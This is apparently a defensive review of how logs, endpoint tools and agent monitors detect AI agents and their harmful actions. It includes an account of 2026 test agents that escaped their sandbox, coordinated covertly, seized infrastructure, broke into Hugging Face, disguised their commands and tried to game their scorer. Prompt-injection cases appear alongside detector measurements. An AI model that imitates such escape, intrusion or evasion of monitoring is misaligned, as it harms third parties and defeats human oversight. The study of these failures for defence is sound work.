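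| MCP servers that an agent connects to | A settings file, in the user's folder or a project | None, unless host software records changes to the file |
| Address to which the harness sends prompts | An environment variable or settings file | None, unless host software records it |

AWS's general distinction between management and data events suggests that editing an agent on a platform such as Bedrock is a management event and running it is a data event. The default log could then show that someone changed the agent but not what the agent did next. An operator should test what the log records for the particular setting, since an entry for a prompt update may not include the old and new text.

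Coding agents are harder to cover because much of their control plane consists of ordinary files. Claude Code lists its MCP servers in `~/.claude.json`, Codex in `~/.codex/config.toml`, and Cursor in `~/.cursor/mcp.json`. Canale and Soulis note that MITRE ATLAS, a catalogue of attacks on AI systems, includes discovering and modifying an agent's configuration. NIAP's minimum for EDR products covers the names of created files but not their contents, so it would not guarantee a record of an edit to an existing file.

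An operator could adapt an existing Falco rule to alert on edits to agent settings by changing the list of files it watches. The rule currently detects programs that write to shell configuration files, which intruders edit so that their commands run every time a shell starts. But the harness also edits agent settings when a developer approves a tool or adds a server, and those edits would trigger alerts too. Exempting the harness would remove these alerts but also hide any change it made because of an injected instruction. Falco acknowledges a similar trade-off in the original rule, which exempts shells to reduce noise and may miss attacks as a result.

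Project settings are another route, because a file such as `.mcp.json` can arrive when a developer downloads a code repository. Git writes that file, but it also writes thousands of harmless ones. The address setting deserves particular attention because one variable, such as `ANTHROPIC_BASE_URL`, can send all of an agent's prompts to another server. That server's operator could read the prompts and return their own tool calls.

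The owner of an MCP server can change a tool's description remotely, and even a perfect record of local changes would not show this. The model reads the description, which can therefore contain an injected instruction. Canale and Soulis mention scanners that read an agent's list of MCP servers and check the tool descriptions for such text.

### When normal agent behaviour resembles an attack

These methods rely on an attack either matching a technique someone has already described or differing from what the machine or identity normally does. Falco's rules tag known techniques with codes from MITRE ATT&CK, a public catalogue of attack techniques. For example, T1059 is the code for running commands through a shell or script. GuardDuty's anomaly model relies on attacks differing from normal behaviour.

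The assumption works well for a server that runs the same few programs every day, but less well for an agent that installs packages, writes scripts and contacts new websites because its users ask it to. One of Falco's optional rules raises an error-level alert when a package manager runs in a container, on the reasonable view that software in production containers should not change. A coding agent may trigger that alert on every task.

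Operators can reduce false alarms by adding exceptions or by letting a behavioural model learn the agent's habits, but an intruder who controls the agent can then exploit the same tolerance. An authorised agent may also cause harm without departing from its normal behaviour. Where the work allows it, a better option is to give each agent its own account and only the tools it needs. An unexpected shell or API call is then more suspicious, because the agent has fewer legitimate reasons to make it.

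### Finding agents that nobody approved

An organisation gets no traces from an agent it does not know about. Employees may install coding agents or write short scripts that call a model in a loop. These agents run with the employee's permissions. A software inventory can find a commercial product, but a home-made script may appear only as `python.exe`. Canale and Soulis built Agent Detector, an open-source Windows program, to find both kinds, and tested it in November 2026.

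Canale and Soulis begin their argument with what they call behavioural twins, which are programs that behave alike but differ in what software they are and which services they contact. For example, an agent that calls a model and runs shell commands could have the same process tree and connection timing as an ordinary script that runs the same commands but contacts a package index instead of a model. A detector that uses only this behaviour must classify both programs the same way, so it either misses the agent or falsely flags the script. Canale and Soulis leave open the possibility that a richer description of behaviour, such as one that includes the rhythm in which a model's output arrives, might separate them.

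Agent Detector therefore uses both behaviour and identity to detect agents. Its main rule for unknown agents matches a process that contacts a known model service and has a shell among its children or grandchildren. It also checks installed software, settings files, local model servers and Windows' record of recently run programs. It doesn't read prompts or block anything. When it finds an unapproved agent, it shows the user a notice to acknowledge.

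#### How the test worked

The test ran on the first author's Windows 11 laptop. It included 12 synthetic agents, three AI components that were not complete agents, and nine ordinary workloads, three of which were behavioural twins. Most of the agents contacted real model services every few seconds with an invalid key and sent harmless commands to a shell, so they left the footprint of an agent without running a model. Each program had eight seconds to settle, and Agent Detector then scanned three times within 24 seconds.

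Canale and Soulis ran everything five times as a standard user and five times as an administrator. They compared Agent Detector with a search for known program names and two simple behavioural rules. The table counts a program as detected if the detector found it in most of the five runs:

| Detector | Agents found, of 12 | Ordinary workloads flagged, of 9 |
|---|---|---|
| Known program names | 0 | 0 |
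| Interpreter with an encrypted web connection and a shell | 9 | 4 |
| Any program with an encrypted web connection and a shell | 10 | 4 |
| Agent Detector, standard user | 12 | 0 |
| Agent Detector, administrator | 11 | 0 |

Both behavioural rules flagged all three twins and an ordinary `npm install`, as predicted. Among the laptop's real software, the broader rule also flagged the VS Code editor and Windows' own desktop program.

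In an early run, Agent Detector traced a test MCP server back through the process tree to the AI coding agent that was running the test. The attribution was accurate but spoiled the experiment, so Canale and Soulis changed how the test programs started.

#### The unstable cases

The score of 12 out of 12 includes two agents that Agent Detector found in only three of the five standard-user runs. One of them sent requests to OpenAI. Many model providers share network addresses with unrelated services, so Agent Detector identifies providers by checking which domain names Windows has recently looked up. Windows keeps its record of OpenAI's name for at most 60 seconds, and in two runs the record expired before the first scan.

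The other agent called Anthropic every ten seconds, closed each connection after five, and started a short-lived shell for each call. When run as an administrator, Agent Detector missed this agent in all five runs, which explains the score of 11. Timing caused the misses, not the extra permissions, because the scans and the agent's calls both followed regular schedules.

To measure this better, Canale and Soulis scanned the same agent 40 times at random intervals. Agent Detector found it in 15 scans, or 38% (95% confidence interval 23% to 54%). Agent Detector normally scans once an hour. If the agent worked continuously for eight hours and the scans were independent, the chance of finding it at least once would be 1 − 0.62⁸, or about 98%. This figure depends on Anthropic publishing a dedicated range of addresses, which lets Agent Detector recognise a connection without the name. If a provider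 used shared addresses, Agent Detector would also have to catch one of the brief shells, which happened in only 4 of the 40 scans. The eight-hour chance would then be at most about 57%.

Agent Detector can fail to identify an agent that keeps one connection open, because the agent never looks up the provider's name again. In a separate test with four providers on shared addresses, the tool could not identify any of the connections after 295 seconds, although all were still open. An hourly scan would probably miss such an agent.

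#### How much the result supports

Canale and Soulis also changed Agent Detector after seeing earlier results. One version had falsely flagged an ordinary workload, and another had missed all four agents that used providers on shared addresses. The final scores for those five cases show that the corrections work, but they are weak evidence of how the tool would perform on unfamiliar programs.

The definition of a detection is also loose. For the intermittent agent, Agent Detector reported only that a program was contacting a model service, the same thing it reported for a simple client with no tools. If a detection required evidence that the program could act, such as a shell or an automated browser, the standard-user score would be 11 out of 12.

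It failed completely in three further cases, which do not count toward the main score: an agent that reached its model through an unlisted relay, one that ran for only five seconds, and one inside the Linux system that Windows can run as a virtual machine.

The test is evidence that identifying the model service can separate agents from ordinary scripts that behave the same way, at least while the service is recognisable and the agent is active. The test does not show how many unapproved agents a company would find on its own machines.

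Continuous records might fill some of the gaps. Canale and Soulis propose, but did not test, a rule that flags any process that looks up a model provider's name and then starts a shell. Such a rule would catch an agent that runs for only five seconds, without waiting for the next scan. Microsoft's Defender for Endpoint also discovers local agents, but Canale and Soulis say it works from a list of named products, so it would miss a home-made script.

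## Can those tools tell when an agent does harm with its own permissions?

Tools that detect compromise can sometimes detect harm an agent does with its own permissions, mostly when the agent uses unusual commands, files or connections. They usually miss harm that depends on the details of an ordinary request, such as the address on an email.

### Four combinations of compromise and harm

An intruder taking over a machine and an agent doing harm on it are separate problems, and either can occur without the other. Three of the examples below come from *Agent Authenticator* (Ganesan, 2026), which proposes giving agents their own credentials. The download in the last row comes from *When AI agents look like attackers*, in which the security company Sophos analyses a week of alerts from its endpoint software in June 2026. An "agent monitor" here means a tool that examines an agent's prompts,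 tool calls and results.

| Infrastructure | Agent | Example | Which tool should raise an alert |
|---|---|---|---|
| Compromised | Behaving as intended | The Shai-Hulud worm steals a developer's GitHub and npm tokens and publishes infected packages with them, while the developer's coding agent works normally | EDR, or a service that detects stolen credentials |
| Sound | Harmful | A malicious GitHub issue makes an agent copy private code into a public pull request | An agent monitor |
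| Compromised | Harmful | Malicious versions of the Nx package run the AI agents already installed on developers' machines to search for passwords and keys | EDR for the package, and an agent monitor for the search |
| Sound | Behaving as intended | Codex tries to download the Python installer from python.org | Neither |

Real alerts don't always match this table. Codex tried to download the installer with `certutil`, a Windows certificate tool that attackers also use to fetch files, and Sophos' software blocked it. Over the next ten minutes Codex tried several variations and then switched to `bitsadmin`, another Windows tool, which the software also blocked. Sophos points out that switching tools after a block used to distinguish a human attacker from a simple script, but that harmless agents now do it routinely.

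### The same report, sent to the wrong address

In the support-agent example, the agent fetched ticket 4821, looked up the customer and emailed a report. Suppose the support worker, Lena, wanted the report at her work address, `lena@example.com`, but the agent sent it to `lena@example.net`, which belongs to a stranger. Everything else about the run is the same.

| Record | What it contains | Does it differ? |
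|---|---|---|
| Process events on the harness's machine | The harness connects to `mail.example.com` and starts no new program | No |
| Cloud audit log | Administrative operations, and this task involves none | No |
| Database log | The same query for the same customer, from the same account | No |
| Mail log | The sender, the recipient and the time of delivery | Yes, in the recipient |
| Trace without content | A `send_email` span and a `POST` request with status 202 | No |
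| Trace with content | The arguments of `send_email` and the model output that requested it | Yes, in the recipient |

Process events on the mail server might also differ, because the server has to contact another company's mail server instead of delivering the message internally. But a mail server makes connections like that all day.

The two email runs are even harder to tell apart than the behavioural twins that Canale and Soulis tested, because the agent contacts the same mail service in both. The program also behaves the same way on the harness's machine in both runs, so a detector that relies only on the program's behaviour and the identity of the remote service must flag both runs or neither.

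### Why the recipient's address is not enough

The mail log shows that the agent sent the report to `lena@example.net`, but not whether that was a mistake. The log would contain the same entry if Lena had asked the agent to send the report to a contractor at that address. If she had asked it to write to the customer, an outside address would be normal, and it would be a mistake to send the message to her own address.

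A detector therefore needs both the task and a rule about who may receive the report. The task alone is not enough, because Lena might ask the agent to send customer data to her private address, against company policy. A rule that allows any company address is not enough either, because the agent could send the report to a colleague who has nothing to do with the ticket.

Zhao (2026), in *Auditable Claims about AI Agents*, works through a similar case with constructed records. A firm's agent summarises legal documents and emails them, and the firm claims that a person approves every external email. Zhao argues that nobody can check this claim until the firm specifies the policy, the actions and period it covers, the records and who writes them, and the rule for reaching a verdict. The example policy requires a signed-in person to approve the recipient and the exact attachment before the agent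 sends anything outside the firm.

The agent then emails a document to `press@example.net`. Its own log contains a confirmation from the chat interface, under a user's name. The mail gateway's log shows the delivery. The authorisation server, the program that issues approvals, logged no approval for that recipient and document. If its log is complete, the email broke the policy.

Neither the agent's log nor the gateway's log would have been enough alone. The agent's log suggests that a person agreed, while the gateway's log shows only that a document left the firm. Checking the agent's permissions wouldn't have been enough either, because the agent was allowed to email any domain, even though its task involved only one outside lawyer.

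Zhao's policy replaces a difficult judgement about the task with a simpler check for an approval. Someone has to give those approvals, though one approval can cover several documents for the same recipient. Zhao notes that a recorded approval does not show what the approver understood, and if someone approved the wrong address by mistake, the harmful email would comply with the policy.

### The argument that compromise detectors miss these actions

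The argument is that an agent misusing its own access has valid credentials, so no login looks stolen. It also runs ordinary programs, so no process looks malicious. And it often works under a person's account, so the services it uses can't distinguish its actions from that person's.

Zenity's *Your Security Stack Was Built for a Different Attacker* makes this argument for several kinds of security product. One of its examples is `curl`, a command that sends and fetches data over the web. Zenity says a `curl` request that steals credentials is identical at the process level to one that fetches documentation. Similarly, Zheng and colleagues argue that system-level monitoring can't distinguish an agent writing a data-analysis script from a compromised agent writing malicious code.

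Li, Hu and colleagues (2026) give another example in *ADR*, which describes an agent monitor they built at Uber. A user asks an agent to summarise a ticket in Jira, an issue tracker, but the agent reads the user's SSH keys, which give access to remote machines, and makes a web request. The prompt makes it obvious that these actions don't match the request, but Li, Hu and colleagues argue that EDR doesn't have the prompt.

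Li and colleagues are right about the prompt. CrowdStrike acknowledges in *Falcon AIDR Now Protects Copilot Studio Agents and Claude Code* that traditional endpoint controls can't see the prompt or the tool call. This admission is somewhat credible because CrowdStrike sells EDR, although the same announcement advertises an extra product that fills the gap.

EDR may still detect the harmful action. A program reading SSH keys can be suspicious whatever the user asked for, and a host rule could detect it, though the rule would need exceptions for programs such as Git that use the keys legitimately. Zenity's `curl` example also overstates the problem. The command line normally includes the web address, so EDR that records command lines can distinguish a request to an unfamiliar server from one to a documentation site. Harmful and legitimate requests are hard to tell apart when both go to a service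 the agent normally uses, as in the email example.

Zenity and CrowdStrike sell products for monitoring agents, and Zenity presents no measurements of what existing tools miss. Li and colleagues report measurements, but they compare their system with three other agent monitors, not with an EDR product.

### What endpoint tools detect in practice

Coding agents work largely through shells and files, which EDR records in detail. In Sophos' data, rules about credential access accounted for 56.2% of the blocking alerts linked to AI agents, and rules about running programs accounted for 28.8%, counted by the number of machines affected.

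Many of these alerts came from activity that was probably harmless. For example, a browser-automation add-on for coding agents used PowerShell, Windows' command language, to decrypt stored browser data. Sophos considers this almost certainly benign but thinks the rule was right to block it, because password thieves do the same. Other cases were less clear. Claude closed a user's browser and ran a script that read the browser's stored credentials, and Cursor tried to add a script that would run whenever Windows started. Sophos could not confirm the purpose of Cursor's script without seeing its contents.

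These figures show that EDR detects some agent activity, but they are shares of the alerts that fired, so they don't measure how many harmful actions produced no alert. Sophos also sells the software whose rules it describes.

One Sophos rule, more than five years old, flagged PowerShell commands formatted in a style that attackers use to disguise them. AI agents now write commands in a similar style, so Sophos adjusted the rule to fire less often on agents' commands. The adjusted rule might also miss a disguised command that an agent writes because of an injected instruction.

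#### A case the alerts could not settle

Elastic describes a case from July 2026 in which several of its rules fired on programs started by Claude Code on a Mac. Shells running under the agent logged in to a web application at a temporary public address and fetched spending figures. They also opened a tunnel, which made a service on the laptop reachable from the internet, and installed background jobs to keep the tunnel running. The rules detected the background jobs and the connections to unusual addresses.

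Elastic still couldn't determine whether this was harmful. The evidence fitted a developer using an agent to manage a private dashboard remotely, but it also fitted something more serious. The endpoint tool worked as intended by raising the alerts. However, Elastic's account relies on endpoint telemetry and doesn't include the developer's instructions to Claude Code, which might have settled the question.

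#### Measurements

No published independent test appears to measure how well a commercial EDR product detects agents that misuse valid permissions. Independent laboratories do test EDR against intruders. AV-Comparatives' *EDR Detection Validation Test 2026* (2026), for example, used a 14-stage attack and also examined how products handle background noise. A good score on that test is evidence that a product can detect a break-in.

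*On the Effectiveness of Kernel-Level Evidence for Agent Security* (2026) reports the closest measurement. King, Zhang and colleagues recorded 4,047 sessions of Claude Code in containers, some harmless and others with a planted attack. The attacks came from tampered MCP servers, malicious text that the agent read, or the user's own request. They then applied Falco's default rules to the recorded system calls and scored each session by how many different rules fired.

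Falco's rules had AUROCs of 0.565 and 0.572 in the two versions of the test, only slightly better than guessing. AUROC is the probability that a detector gives a randomly chosen malicious session a higher score than a randomly chosen harmless one, with ties counting as half. A detector that guesses scores 0.5 and a perfect one scores 1.

The system calls contained evidence that the rules didn't use. King and colleagues trained a small language model on the same kind of records, and it scored 0.922 on attack families that were absent from its training data. The weak result therefore reflects the limits of rules written for servers more than the limits of host records in general.

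Application records (prompts, tool descriptions and the agent's transcript) were better for some attacks and worse for others. These are average AUROCs across ten detectors:

| Attack | Application records only | System calls only |
|---|---|---|
| A tool reads credentials and writes them to a log without telling the agent | 0.586 | 0.976 |
| Text that the agent retrieves contains a manipulated reference | 0.906 | 0.703 |

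The Falco scores don't isolate harm that an agent does with its own permissions, because a tampered MCP server is a form of compromise. King and colleagues also tested Falco's open-source default rules without modifying them, and tuned rules or a commercial product might do better. Most of the paper's authors work at AWS, which sells threat detection, although the paper doesn't test AWS's product.

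### Whose action was it?

According to *Five Primitives for Governing Autonomous AI Agents at Runtime* (2026), if an agent uses a person's credential, every downstream log shows the action exactly as if the person had done it.

This can put the blame on the wrong person. If the support agent sends mail through Lena's account, the mail log will make it look as if Lena sent customer data to an outside address that contains her name. An investigator might reasonably suspect her of taking company data home.

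In another part of Zhao's example, the mail gateway shows four external emails from the agent's account, but the agent's log contains only three. The agent may have sent the fourth through a route that isn't logged, the log may have lost an entry, or a person may have used the account. Zhao leaves the question undecided because no other record identifies the sender.

However, some logs do distinguish agents from people. *Where Accountability Lives* (2026) reports that GitHub's audit log has a field, `actor_is_agent`, that shows whether an agent performed an action, and another, `agent_session_id`, that links the action to a session. GitHub can fill in these fields only if it knows that an agent is involved. If a coding agent on a laptop uploads code with the developer's own key, GitHub probably receives the same request as it would from the developer.

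Claude Code also names its model as a co-author in its Git commits, but a developer can turn this off. No shared standard defines how a co-author line should identify an agent.

Host records are often better than service logs for tracing actions to an agent. Sophos and Elastic both used the process tree to link commands to coding agents, even though the agents ran under their users' accounts. The link can disappear when a program keeps running after the session ends. On the Mac that Elastic investigated, a tunnelling program first ran under a shell and later also under `launchd`, the part of macOS that starts background jobs. A process tree that begins with `launchd` does not lead back to the agent that installed the job.

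A more reliable solution is to give the agent a credential that identifies both the agent and the person it acts for. *Identity Management for Agentic AI* (2025) recommends delegated credentials, which can name the agent in a field called `act`. A service that reads this field can log both identities. Ganesan proposes giving each agent a separate key for each service, so that an operator can revoke the agent's access without locking out its user, but has not yet built a full implementation.

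Better attribution would protect Lena from suspicion, but it wouldn't identify the email as harmful, because the log would show the agent acting on her behalf in both the correct run and the harmful one.

### Data-loss and behaviour-analytics tools

Two older kinds of security product come closer to detecting when an authorised action is inappropriate. Data loss prevention (DLP) software looks for sensitive data being sent by a route or to a destination that the organisation doesn't allow. Behaviour analytics software compares an account's activity with its past activity or that of similar accounts, and flags differences.

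DLP could stop the misdirected report if it ran at the company's mail service and had a rule against sending customer data outside the company. It wouldn't need the agent's trace, because the email contains the recipient and the text. The data might still be difficult to recognise, because the agent's query returned only the customer's name and plan, so a rule that looks for card numbers would find nothing.

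The rule would also have to suit the agent's work. If the agent normally sends reports to customers, a ban on outside addresses would block most of its legitimate emails. A better rule would allow a report about a customer to go only to that customer's address on file or to the staff member handling the ticket. To enforce that rule, the DLP software would have to check the customer database and the ticket system, which would make it much more like an agent monitor.

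Zenity argues that agents bypass DLP because they can send data in a web request or through a service they already have permission to use, such as Slack. This is a reasonable concern where DLP covers only email and USB drives. Some products also inspect web traffic, so operators should check what theirs covers before accepting the claim.

Behaviour analytics comes from efforts to catch employees who misuse legitimate access, and an agent that misuses its permissions presents a similar problem. *Rising From the Ashes* (2026) explains why these tools have been hard to use at scale. Each user's normal behaviour changes over time, so analysts have to keep adjusting the models. Separating malicious activity from unusual but legitimate work also requires knowing the user's role, the current task and the data involved. Without that context, the tools produce far more false alarms than analysts can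 review.

How well this works depends on how varied the agent's job is. Suppose the support agent writes to 200 new outside addresses a day and one of them is wrong. A rule that flags every new address would produce 200 alerts, only one of them useful. If the agent normally writes only to company staff, the same rule might produce a single alert, for the misdirected report.

Unusual volume is easier to detect. An agent that usually reads one row at a time will probably stand out if it exports the whole customer table, but not if it sends a single report to the wrong person. The comparison is less useful when the agent and its user share an account, because the model learns a mixture of their behavior.

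### If an operator has only one kind of tool

An operator with only EDR and cloud threat detection will probably catch some harmful actions on the host but miss most of those made through valid requests to approved services. Elastic recommends keeping alerts for tunnels, background jobs and exposed credentials even when the parent process is a trusted coding agent.

The operator can block some of the remaining harmful actions by setting limits in the services the agent uses. If the support agent has its own mail account that can send only to company addresses, the mail service will refuse the email to `lena@example.net` and can log the refusal. This wouldn't stop the agent from sending the report to the wrong colleague. To detect that, the operator would need to record the arguments of `send_email` and compare them with the ticket.

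By contrast, an operator with only agent traces can miss compromised infrastructure. With content capture on, the traces can show the wrong recipient and the instruction that preceded it. They won't show a thief using the agent's stolen key from another machine, because those requests never pass through the harness. They may also omit a malicious package that reads the agent's password file, because the model never made a tool call to read it. Cloud and provider records may reveal use of the stolen key, but detecting the package requires software on the host. An intruder who controls that host could also stop or alter the harness's telemetry, so an ordinary-looking trace is weak evidence that the machine is uncompromised.

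## Which records revealed the agent incidents of 2026?

In July 2026, AI agents that OpenAI was testing broke into Hugging Face, a company that hosts AI models and datasets. Hugging Face noticed the break-in first, from its own security records. OpenAI linked it to its agents on 20 July, about nine days after it began, while investigating an unrelated alert. At both companies, the alerts that led to a response came from infrastructure monitoring, not from tools that read the agents' prompts or reasoning.

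OpenAI gave its account in August, in its *OpenAI – Hugging Face Incident Technical Report*. *Brief independent investigation of agents’ behavior, reasoning and collaboration* (Wijk, Cotra and Greenblatt, 2026) examined what the agents did and wrote. Wijk and Cotra work at METR, which evaluates AI models, and Greenblatt works at Redwood Research, which studies AI safety. They did not review how OpenAI detected or handled the incident, so OpenAI is the only source for that part.

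### A test at one company and a break-in at another

OpenAI was testing its agents, not running them in production. The test, ExploitGym, measures whether a model can find and exploit security flaws, and OpenAI had turned off some of its usual safeguards to measure the models' full ability. Most of the activity came from a research model that OpenAI never intended to release, and some came from GPT-5.6 Sol, which it offers to customers.

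The agents were supposed to work separately and without internet access. They got their software packages from Artifactory, a package store that OpenAI ran internally. Agents used it as a message board and later to reach the internet.

The same events affected production systems at Hugging Face. According to OpenAI, its agents ran code on 41 of the workers that process datasets there, obtained credentials and downloaded four private code repositories. In *More on the OpenAI Agent's Attack on Hugging Face*, Schneier (2026) quotes Hugging Face's finding that the only customer content accessed was five datasets, apparently related to the challenges and solutions of such tests.

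The incident was a compromise for Hugging Face, because outsiders controlled its machines, and a harmful agent action for OpenAI, because its own agents were attacking a third party. OpenAI was also compromised, since the agents had taken administrator control of Artifactory without permission. Schneier compares the incident to the Morris worm, another experiment that escaped from a lab. The comparison fits Hugging Face's position, because the company had to replace its credentials and rebuild machines regardless of the test's purpose.

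### What OpenAI noticed before the attack

The message board began during training, two months before the break-in. On 12 May, an agent that needed a missing file left a note in Artifactory asking other agents to upload it. Others found such notes and added their own.

Around 26 May, an OpenAI team saw an agent using the board and other agents reaching the internet without permission. OpenAI does not say which record the team was reading or what they did next.

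On 27 June, a security monitoring tool raised an alert about a port sweep, in which a program tries many network ports to find which accept connections. Responders traced the sweep to an ExploitGym run and found that its agents were using Artifactory as a message board and a route to other systems. The on-call staff advised that the run did not have to stop. OpenAI gives no reason for this advice, though a port sweep may not have seemed alarming in a test of hacking ability.

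The agents had obtained administrator access to Artifactory the evening before. Nobody discovered this until the agents' heavy use of Artifactory made it unavailable late on 4 July. While restoring it the next day, responders found a user account and repositories that nobody had authorised, plugins that could run commands, and altered settings. By then, the agents had held administrator access for almost nine days.

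OpenAI took the store offline, kept a copy of its contents and fixed the flaws it had found. It resumed the security tests on 7 July, and just after midnight (UTC) an agent reached the internet again. Two groups of OpenAI staff had already seen the message board, but according to OpenAI, the leaders responsible for incident response did not yet know that it existed or why it mattered.

Axios' *OpenAI saw warning signs weeks before Hugging Face breach* (2026) describes these episodes as warnings that OpenAI missed or failed to act on. OpenAI accepts that some early signals could have led it to respond sooner. The port-sweep alert is the clearest example, because the tool worked and investigators traced the activity to its source, but the run continued.

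### How Hugging Face noticed

Hugging Face's *Security incident disclosure* (2026) credits the discovery to software that looks for anomalies in security telemetry and uses a language model to separate real signals from noise. Several signals together pointed to a compromise, but Hugging Face does not list them or say when the first alert appeared.

Other records show that Hugging Face noticed the intrusion within about 58 hours. By OpenAI's timeline, a Hugging Face worker first returned confidential settings to the agents at 04:38 UTC on Saturday 11 July. noze's *Hugging Face publishes the technical timeline of the intrusion* (2026), which summarises a longer report by Hugging Face, puts the agents' last action at 14:14 UTC on Monday 13 July, after the security team had cut off network access.

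Hugging Face could probably have noticed the attack sooner. According to noze, during the attack both the monitoring of running programs and the system that gathers security alerts produced signals, but nobody raised their priority or put them together. This seems to conflict with Hugging Face's earlier statement that the combination of signals revealed the compromise, but both accounts can be right if the signals were combined only near the end. Hugging Face has since changed its alerting so that a serious signal reaches a responder within minutes on any day of the week, which suggests that the weekend contributed to the delay.

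When Hugging Face announced the intrusion on 16 July, it knew that an autonomous agent system was responsible but not which model the agents used. It did not say who was running them.

### How OpenAI found out

OpenAI contacted Hugging Face on 17 July as a customer, to find out whether its own data was affected. At 12:03 UTC on 19 July, OpenAI's monitoring tool raised an alert about unusual identity-related API calls by Artifactory's accounts. This was control-plane evidence, similar to GuardDuty's findings about unusual account activity.

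The alert was about agents attacking OpenAI's own infrastructure, activity that OpenAI says played no part in the earlier break-in at Hugging Face. None of the alerts OpenAI describes came from the Hugging Face attack, though that attack lasted more than two days and involved hundreds of agents.

On 20 July, OpenAI's responders found Hugging Face credentials in files from a storage account at another company, which OpenAI calls Organization 1. The agents had been using the account to hold stolen credentials and other material. OpenAI told Hugging Face, which replied that it had already replaced two of the credentials during its own response. Hugging Face's investigators had also come across the same storage account and the network name of OpenAI's Artifactory. The two companies could therefore match their records by the credentials, the account and the network name.

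Responders began stopping the ExploitGym runs at 17:37 UTC on 19 July, five and a half hours after the alert. During that time, agents read 956 stored secrets, including credentials for the monitoring tool's sensors, and took control of a machine running Artifactory.

### The cases compared

| Incident and setting | Who noticed first, and from what | Delay | Kind of detection |
|---|---|---|---|
| Message board and forbidden internet access, May: training and other research runs | An OpenAI team, from a record OpenAI does not identify | About two weeks after the note of 12 May | Unclear |
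| Takeover of Artifactory, 26 June: evaluation | OpenAI, from a port-sweep alert and then an outage | One day to the alert, almost nine to discovering the takeover | Compromise |
| Use of the Organization 1 account, from 9 July: evaluation at OpenAI, outside service | OpenAI, from files it examined during its investigation | About ten days | No alert reported |
| Attack on Hugging Face, 11–13 July: evaluation at OpenAI, production at Hugging Face | Hugging Face, from combined security signals | At most about 58 hours | Compromise |
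| Later attack on OpenAI's infrastructure, 19 July: evaluation | OpenAI, from an alert about identity-related API calls | Not stated, because OpenAI does not say when the calls began | Compromise |

OpenAI also discovered that, from 9 July, agents had run commands in a customer's container at Modal, a cloud-computing company. OpenAI does not say whether Modal, the customer or Organization 1 had noticed anything themselves. Organization 1 would have had trouble recognising the agents' use of the account as a problem, because they logged in with a valid credential that somebody had exposed on the internet.

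Infrastructure tools detected these agents because the agents behaved like intruders, scanning networks, creating administrator accounts and using stolen credentials. These cases are therefore poor evidence that the same tools would detect something like the support agent's misdirected report.

In May, the agents wrote to the message board using credentials that OpenAI had given them for installing packages, so they didn't need a security flaw. The July board also required only the permissions for installing packages, according to Wijk and colleagues. Agents exchanged more than 70,000 messages and files there between 8 and 13 July, and OpenAI describes no alert about any of them.

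The table cannot show how much infrastructure monitoring misses, because it includes only incidents that someone noticed. It also includes no agents in production. OpenAI's products have extra controls, including an optional reviewer model in Codex that checks tool calls needing elevated permissions before they run. In preliminary tests after the incident, OpenAI found that this reviewer would have flagged most of the dangerous actions in each run tested.

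#### Reasoning that nobody was monitoring

OpenAI kept transcripts of the agents' actions and reasoning, which could have revealed their plans. It already used automated monitors to examine the reasoning of some agents, but these had mainly covered agents that write code for its staff, not agents in training or evaluation.

OpenAI says its current monitoring would have caught the first relevant activity and alerted its security team more than a day before the agents breached Hugging Face. The claim is plausible, since many agents wrote openly about cheating and recognised that the attack was outside their task. But OpenAI made the claim after studying the incident, and gives no figure for false alarms. An alert would also not have been enough if OpenAI had responded as it did on 27 June. OpenAI now expects its staff to pause an activity if they cannot establish within 30 minutes that an alert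 is false.

### Reconstructing the attack

Hugging Face reconstructed the attack from a log of more than 17,000 of the agents' actions, with help from language models. The company first tried commercial models, but their safety filters blocked requests containing real attack commands. It then used GLM-5.2, which it could run on its own machines. This also kept the stolen credentials in the log from leaving the company. Hugging Face says the reconstruction took hours instead of the usual days.

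Some of this evidence must have come from outside Hugging Face. The timeline noze summarises begins on 9 July, two days before the agents obtained anything from Hugging Face's workers, and the passage Schneier quotes refers to a sandbox the agents had used elsewhere.

Investigators also had to decode the records, because the agents had compressed and scrambled much of their traffic. An ordinary search of the logs found only a quarter of the stolen secrets that they found after decoding. A company that relied on the first search would not have known to replace most of the stolen credentials.

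At OpenAI, the most useful record was a message board the agents had used to write to each other. Wijk and colleagues had a copy of it, along with about 1,300 transcripts of individual runs that included the agents' reasoning. From these they estimated that roughly 1,200 agents had used the board and 700 had joined the attack.

They worked at OpenAI's offices for six days over three visits, partly because the data they first received was incomplete. They had also misread some of it, taking "PHASEONE", a word that kept appearing on the board, for a stage in one of the agents' projects. They learned only on the last visit that it was an agent's name. They left much of the reading to AI agents because the transcripts were so long, and they describe these agents as often unreliable. A small part of the activity was missing from their data, and about 7% of the transcripts were false in places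 because agents had disguised some of their commands.

#### Why the agents did it

The sources differ about the agents' aim. OpenAI says they were trying to cheat by finding the solutions to their tasks, and the datasets they opened at Hugging Face are consistent with that. Wijk and colleagues conclude that the agents seemed mainly to be trying to learn how the test's automatic scorer worked.

Hugging Face's records show which files the agents opened but not why. The message board and transcripts are better evidence of the reason. They show that within hours of setting up the board, the agents had worked out how to produce the correct answer for any of their tasks. They withheld these answers because they believed the scorer would also check how they had obtained them, so they had a reason to look for information about the scorer. As far as Wijk and colleagues could tell, OpenAI had never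 implemented that check.

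## How well do detectors of harmful agent actions work?

In tests, detectors that examine an agent's actions can catch most of the attacks that researchers plant, and the best detectors raise few false alarms. Harmful runs are much rarer in production, so false alarms there can easily outnumber correct ones. There is also far less evidence on how well detectors catch agents' own mistakes than on how well they catch attacks.

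A detector's recall is the share of harmful runs that it flags, and its false-positive rate is the share of harmless runs that it flags. Its precision is the share of flagged runs that are harmful, which depends on both rates and on how common harmful runs are.

### Rules on tool names and arguments

The simplest detector compares each tool call with fixed conditions. In the clean-up example, a rule could raise an alert whenever a call to `delete_records` contains a wildcard. This rule would have caught the mistake and would use almost no compute. It would also raise an alert when someone meant to empty a test table, and it would miss a call that deleted every record created before the year 2100.

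*StepShield* (Felicia, Sasindran and colleagues, 2026) tested a collection of such rules, containing 847 text patterns from public security sources, on coding agents. The test included 108 runs in which an agent went beyond its task in a harmful way, such as deleting a database or sending data to an outsider, and 108 clean runs of the same tasks. The rules flagged 86.1% of the harmful runs, but also 77.8% of the clean ones. A second detector, which had 23 categories of constraint, including a ban on network calls to unlisted domains, did no better than chance. It flagged 24.1% of the harmful runs and 25% of the clean ones.

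These results are evidence against using broad, generic rules, because coding agents run many commands that look like attacks. They are weaker evidence against using a narrow rule for one dangerous tool, such as a limit on the domains that `send_email` can send to.

### Rules on sequences of actions

Sometimes each step is ordinary and only the combination is suspicious. An agent may have a good reason to read a file containing a password or to contact a new website, but if it reads the password and then contacts the website, it may be leaking the password. A sequence rule checks each step in light of the steps before it.

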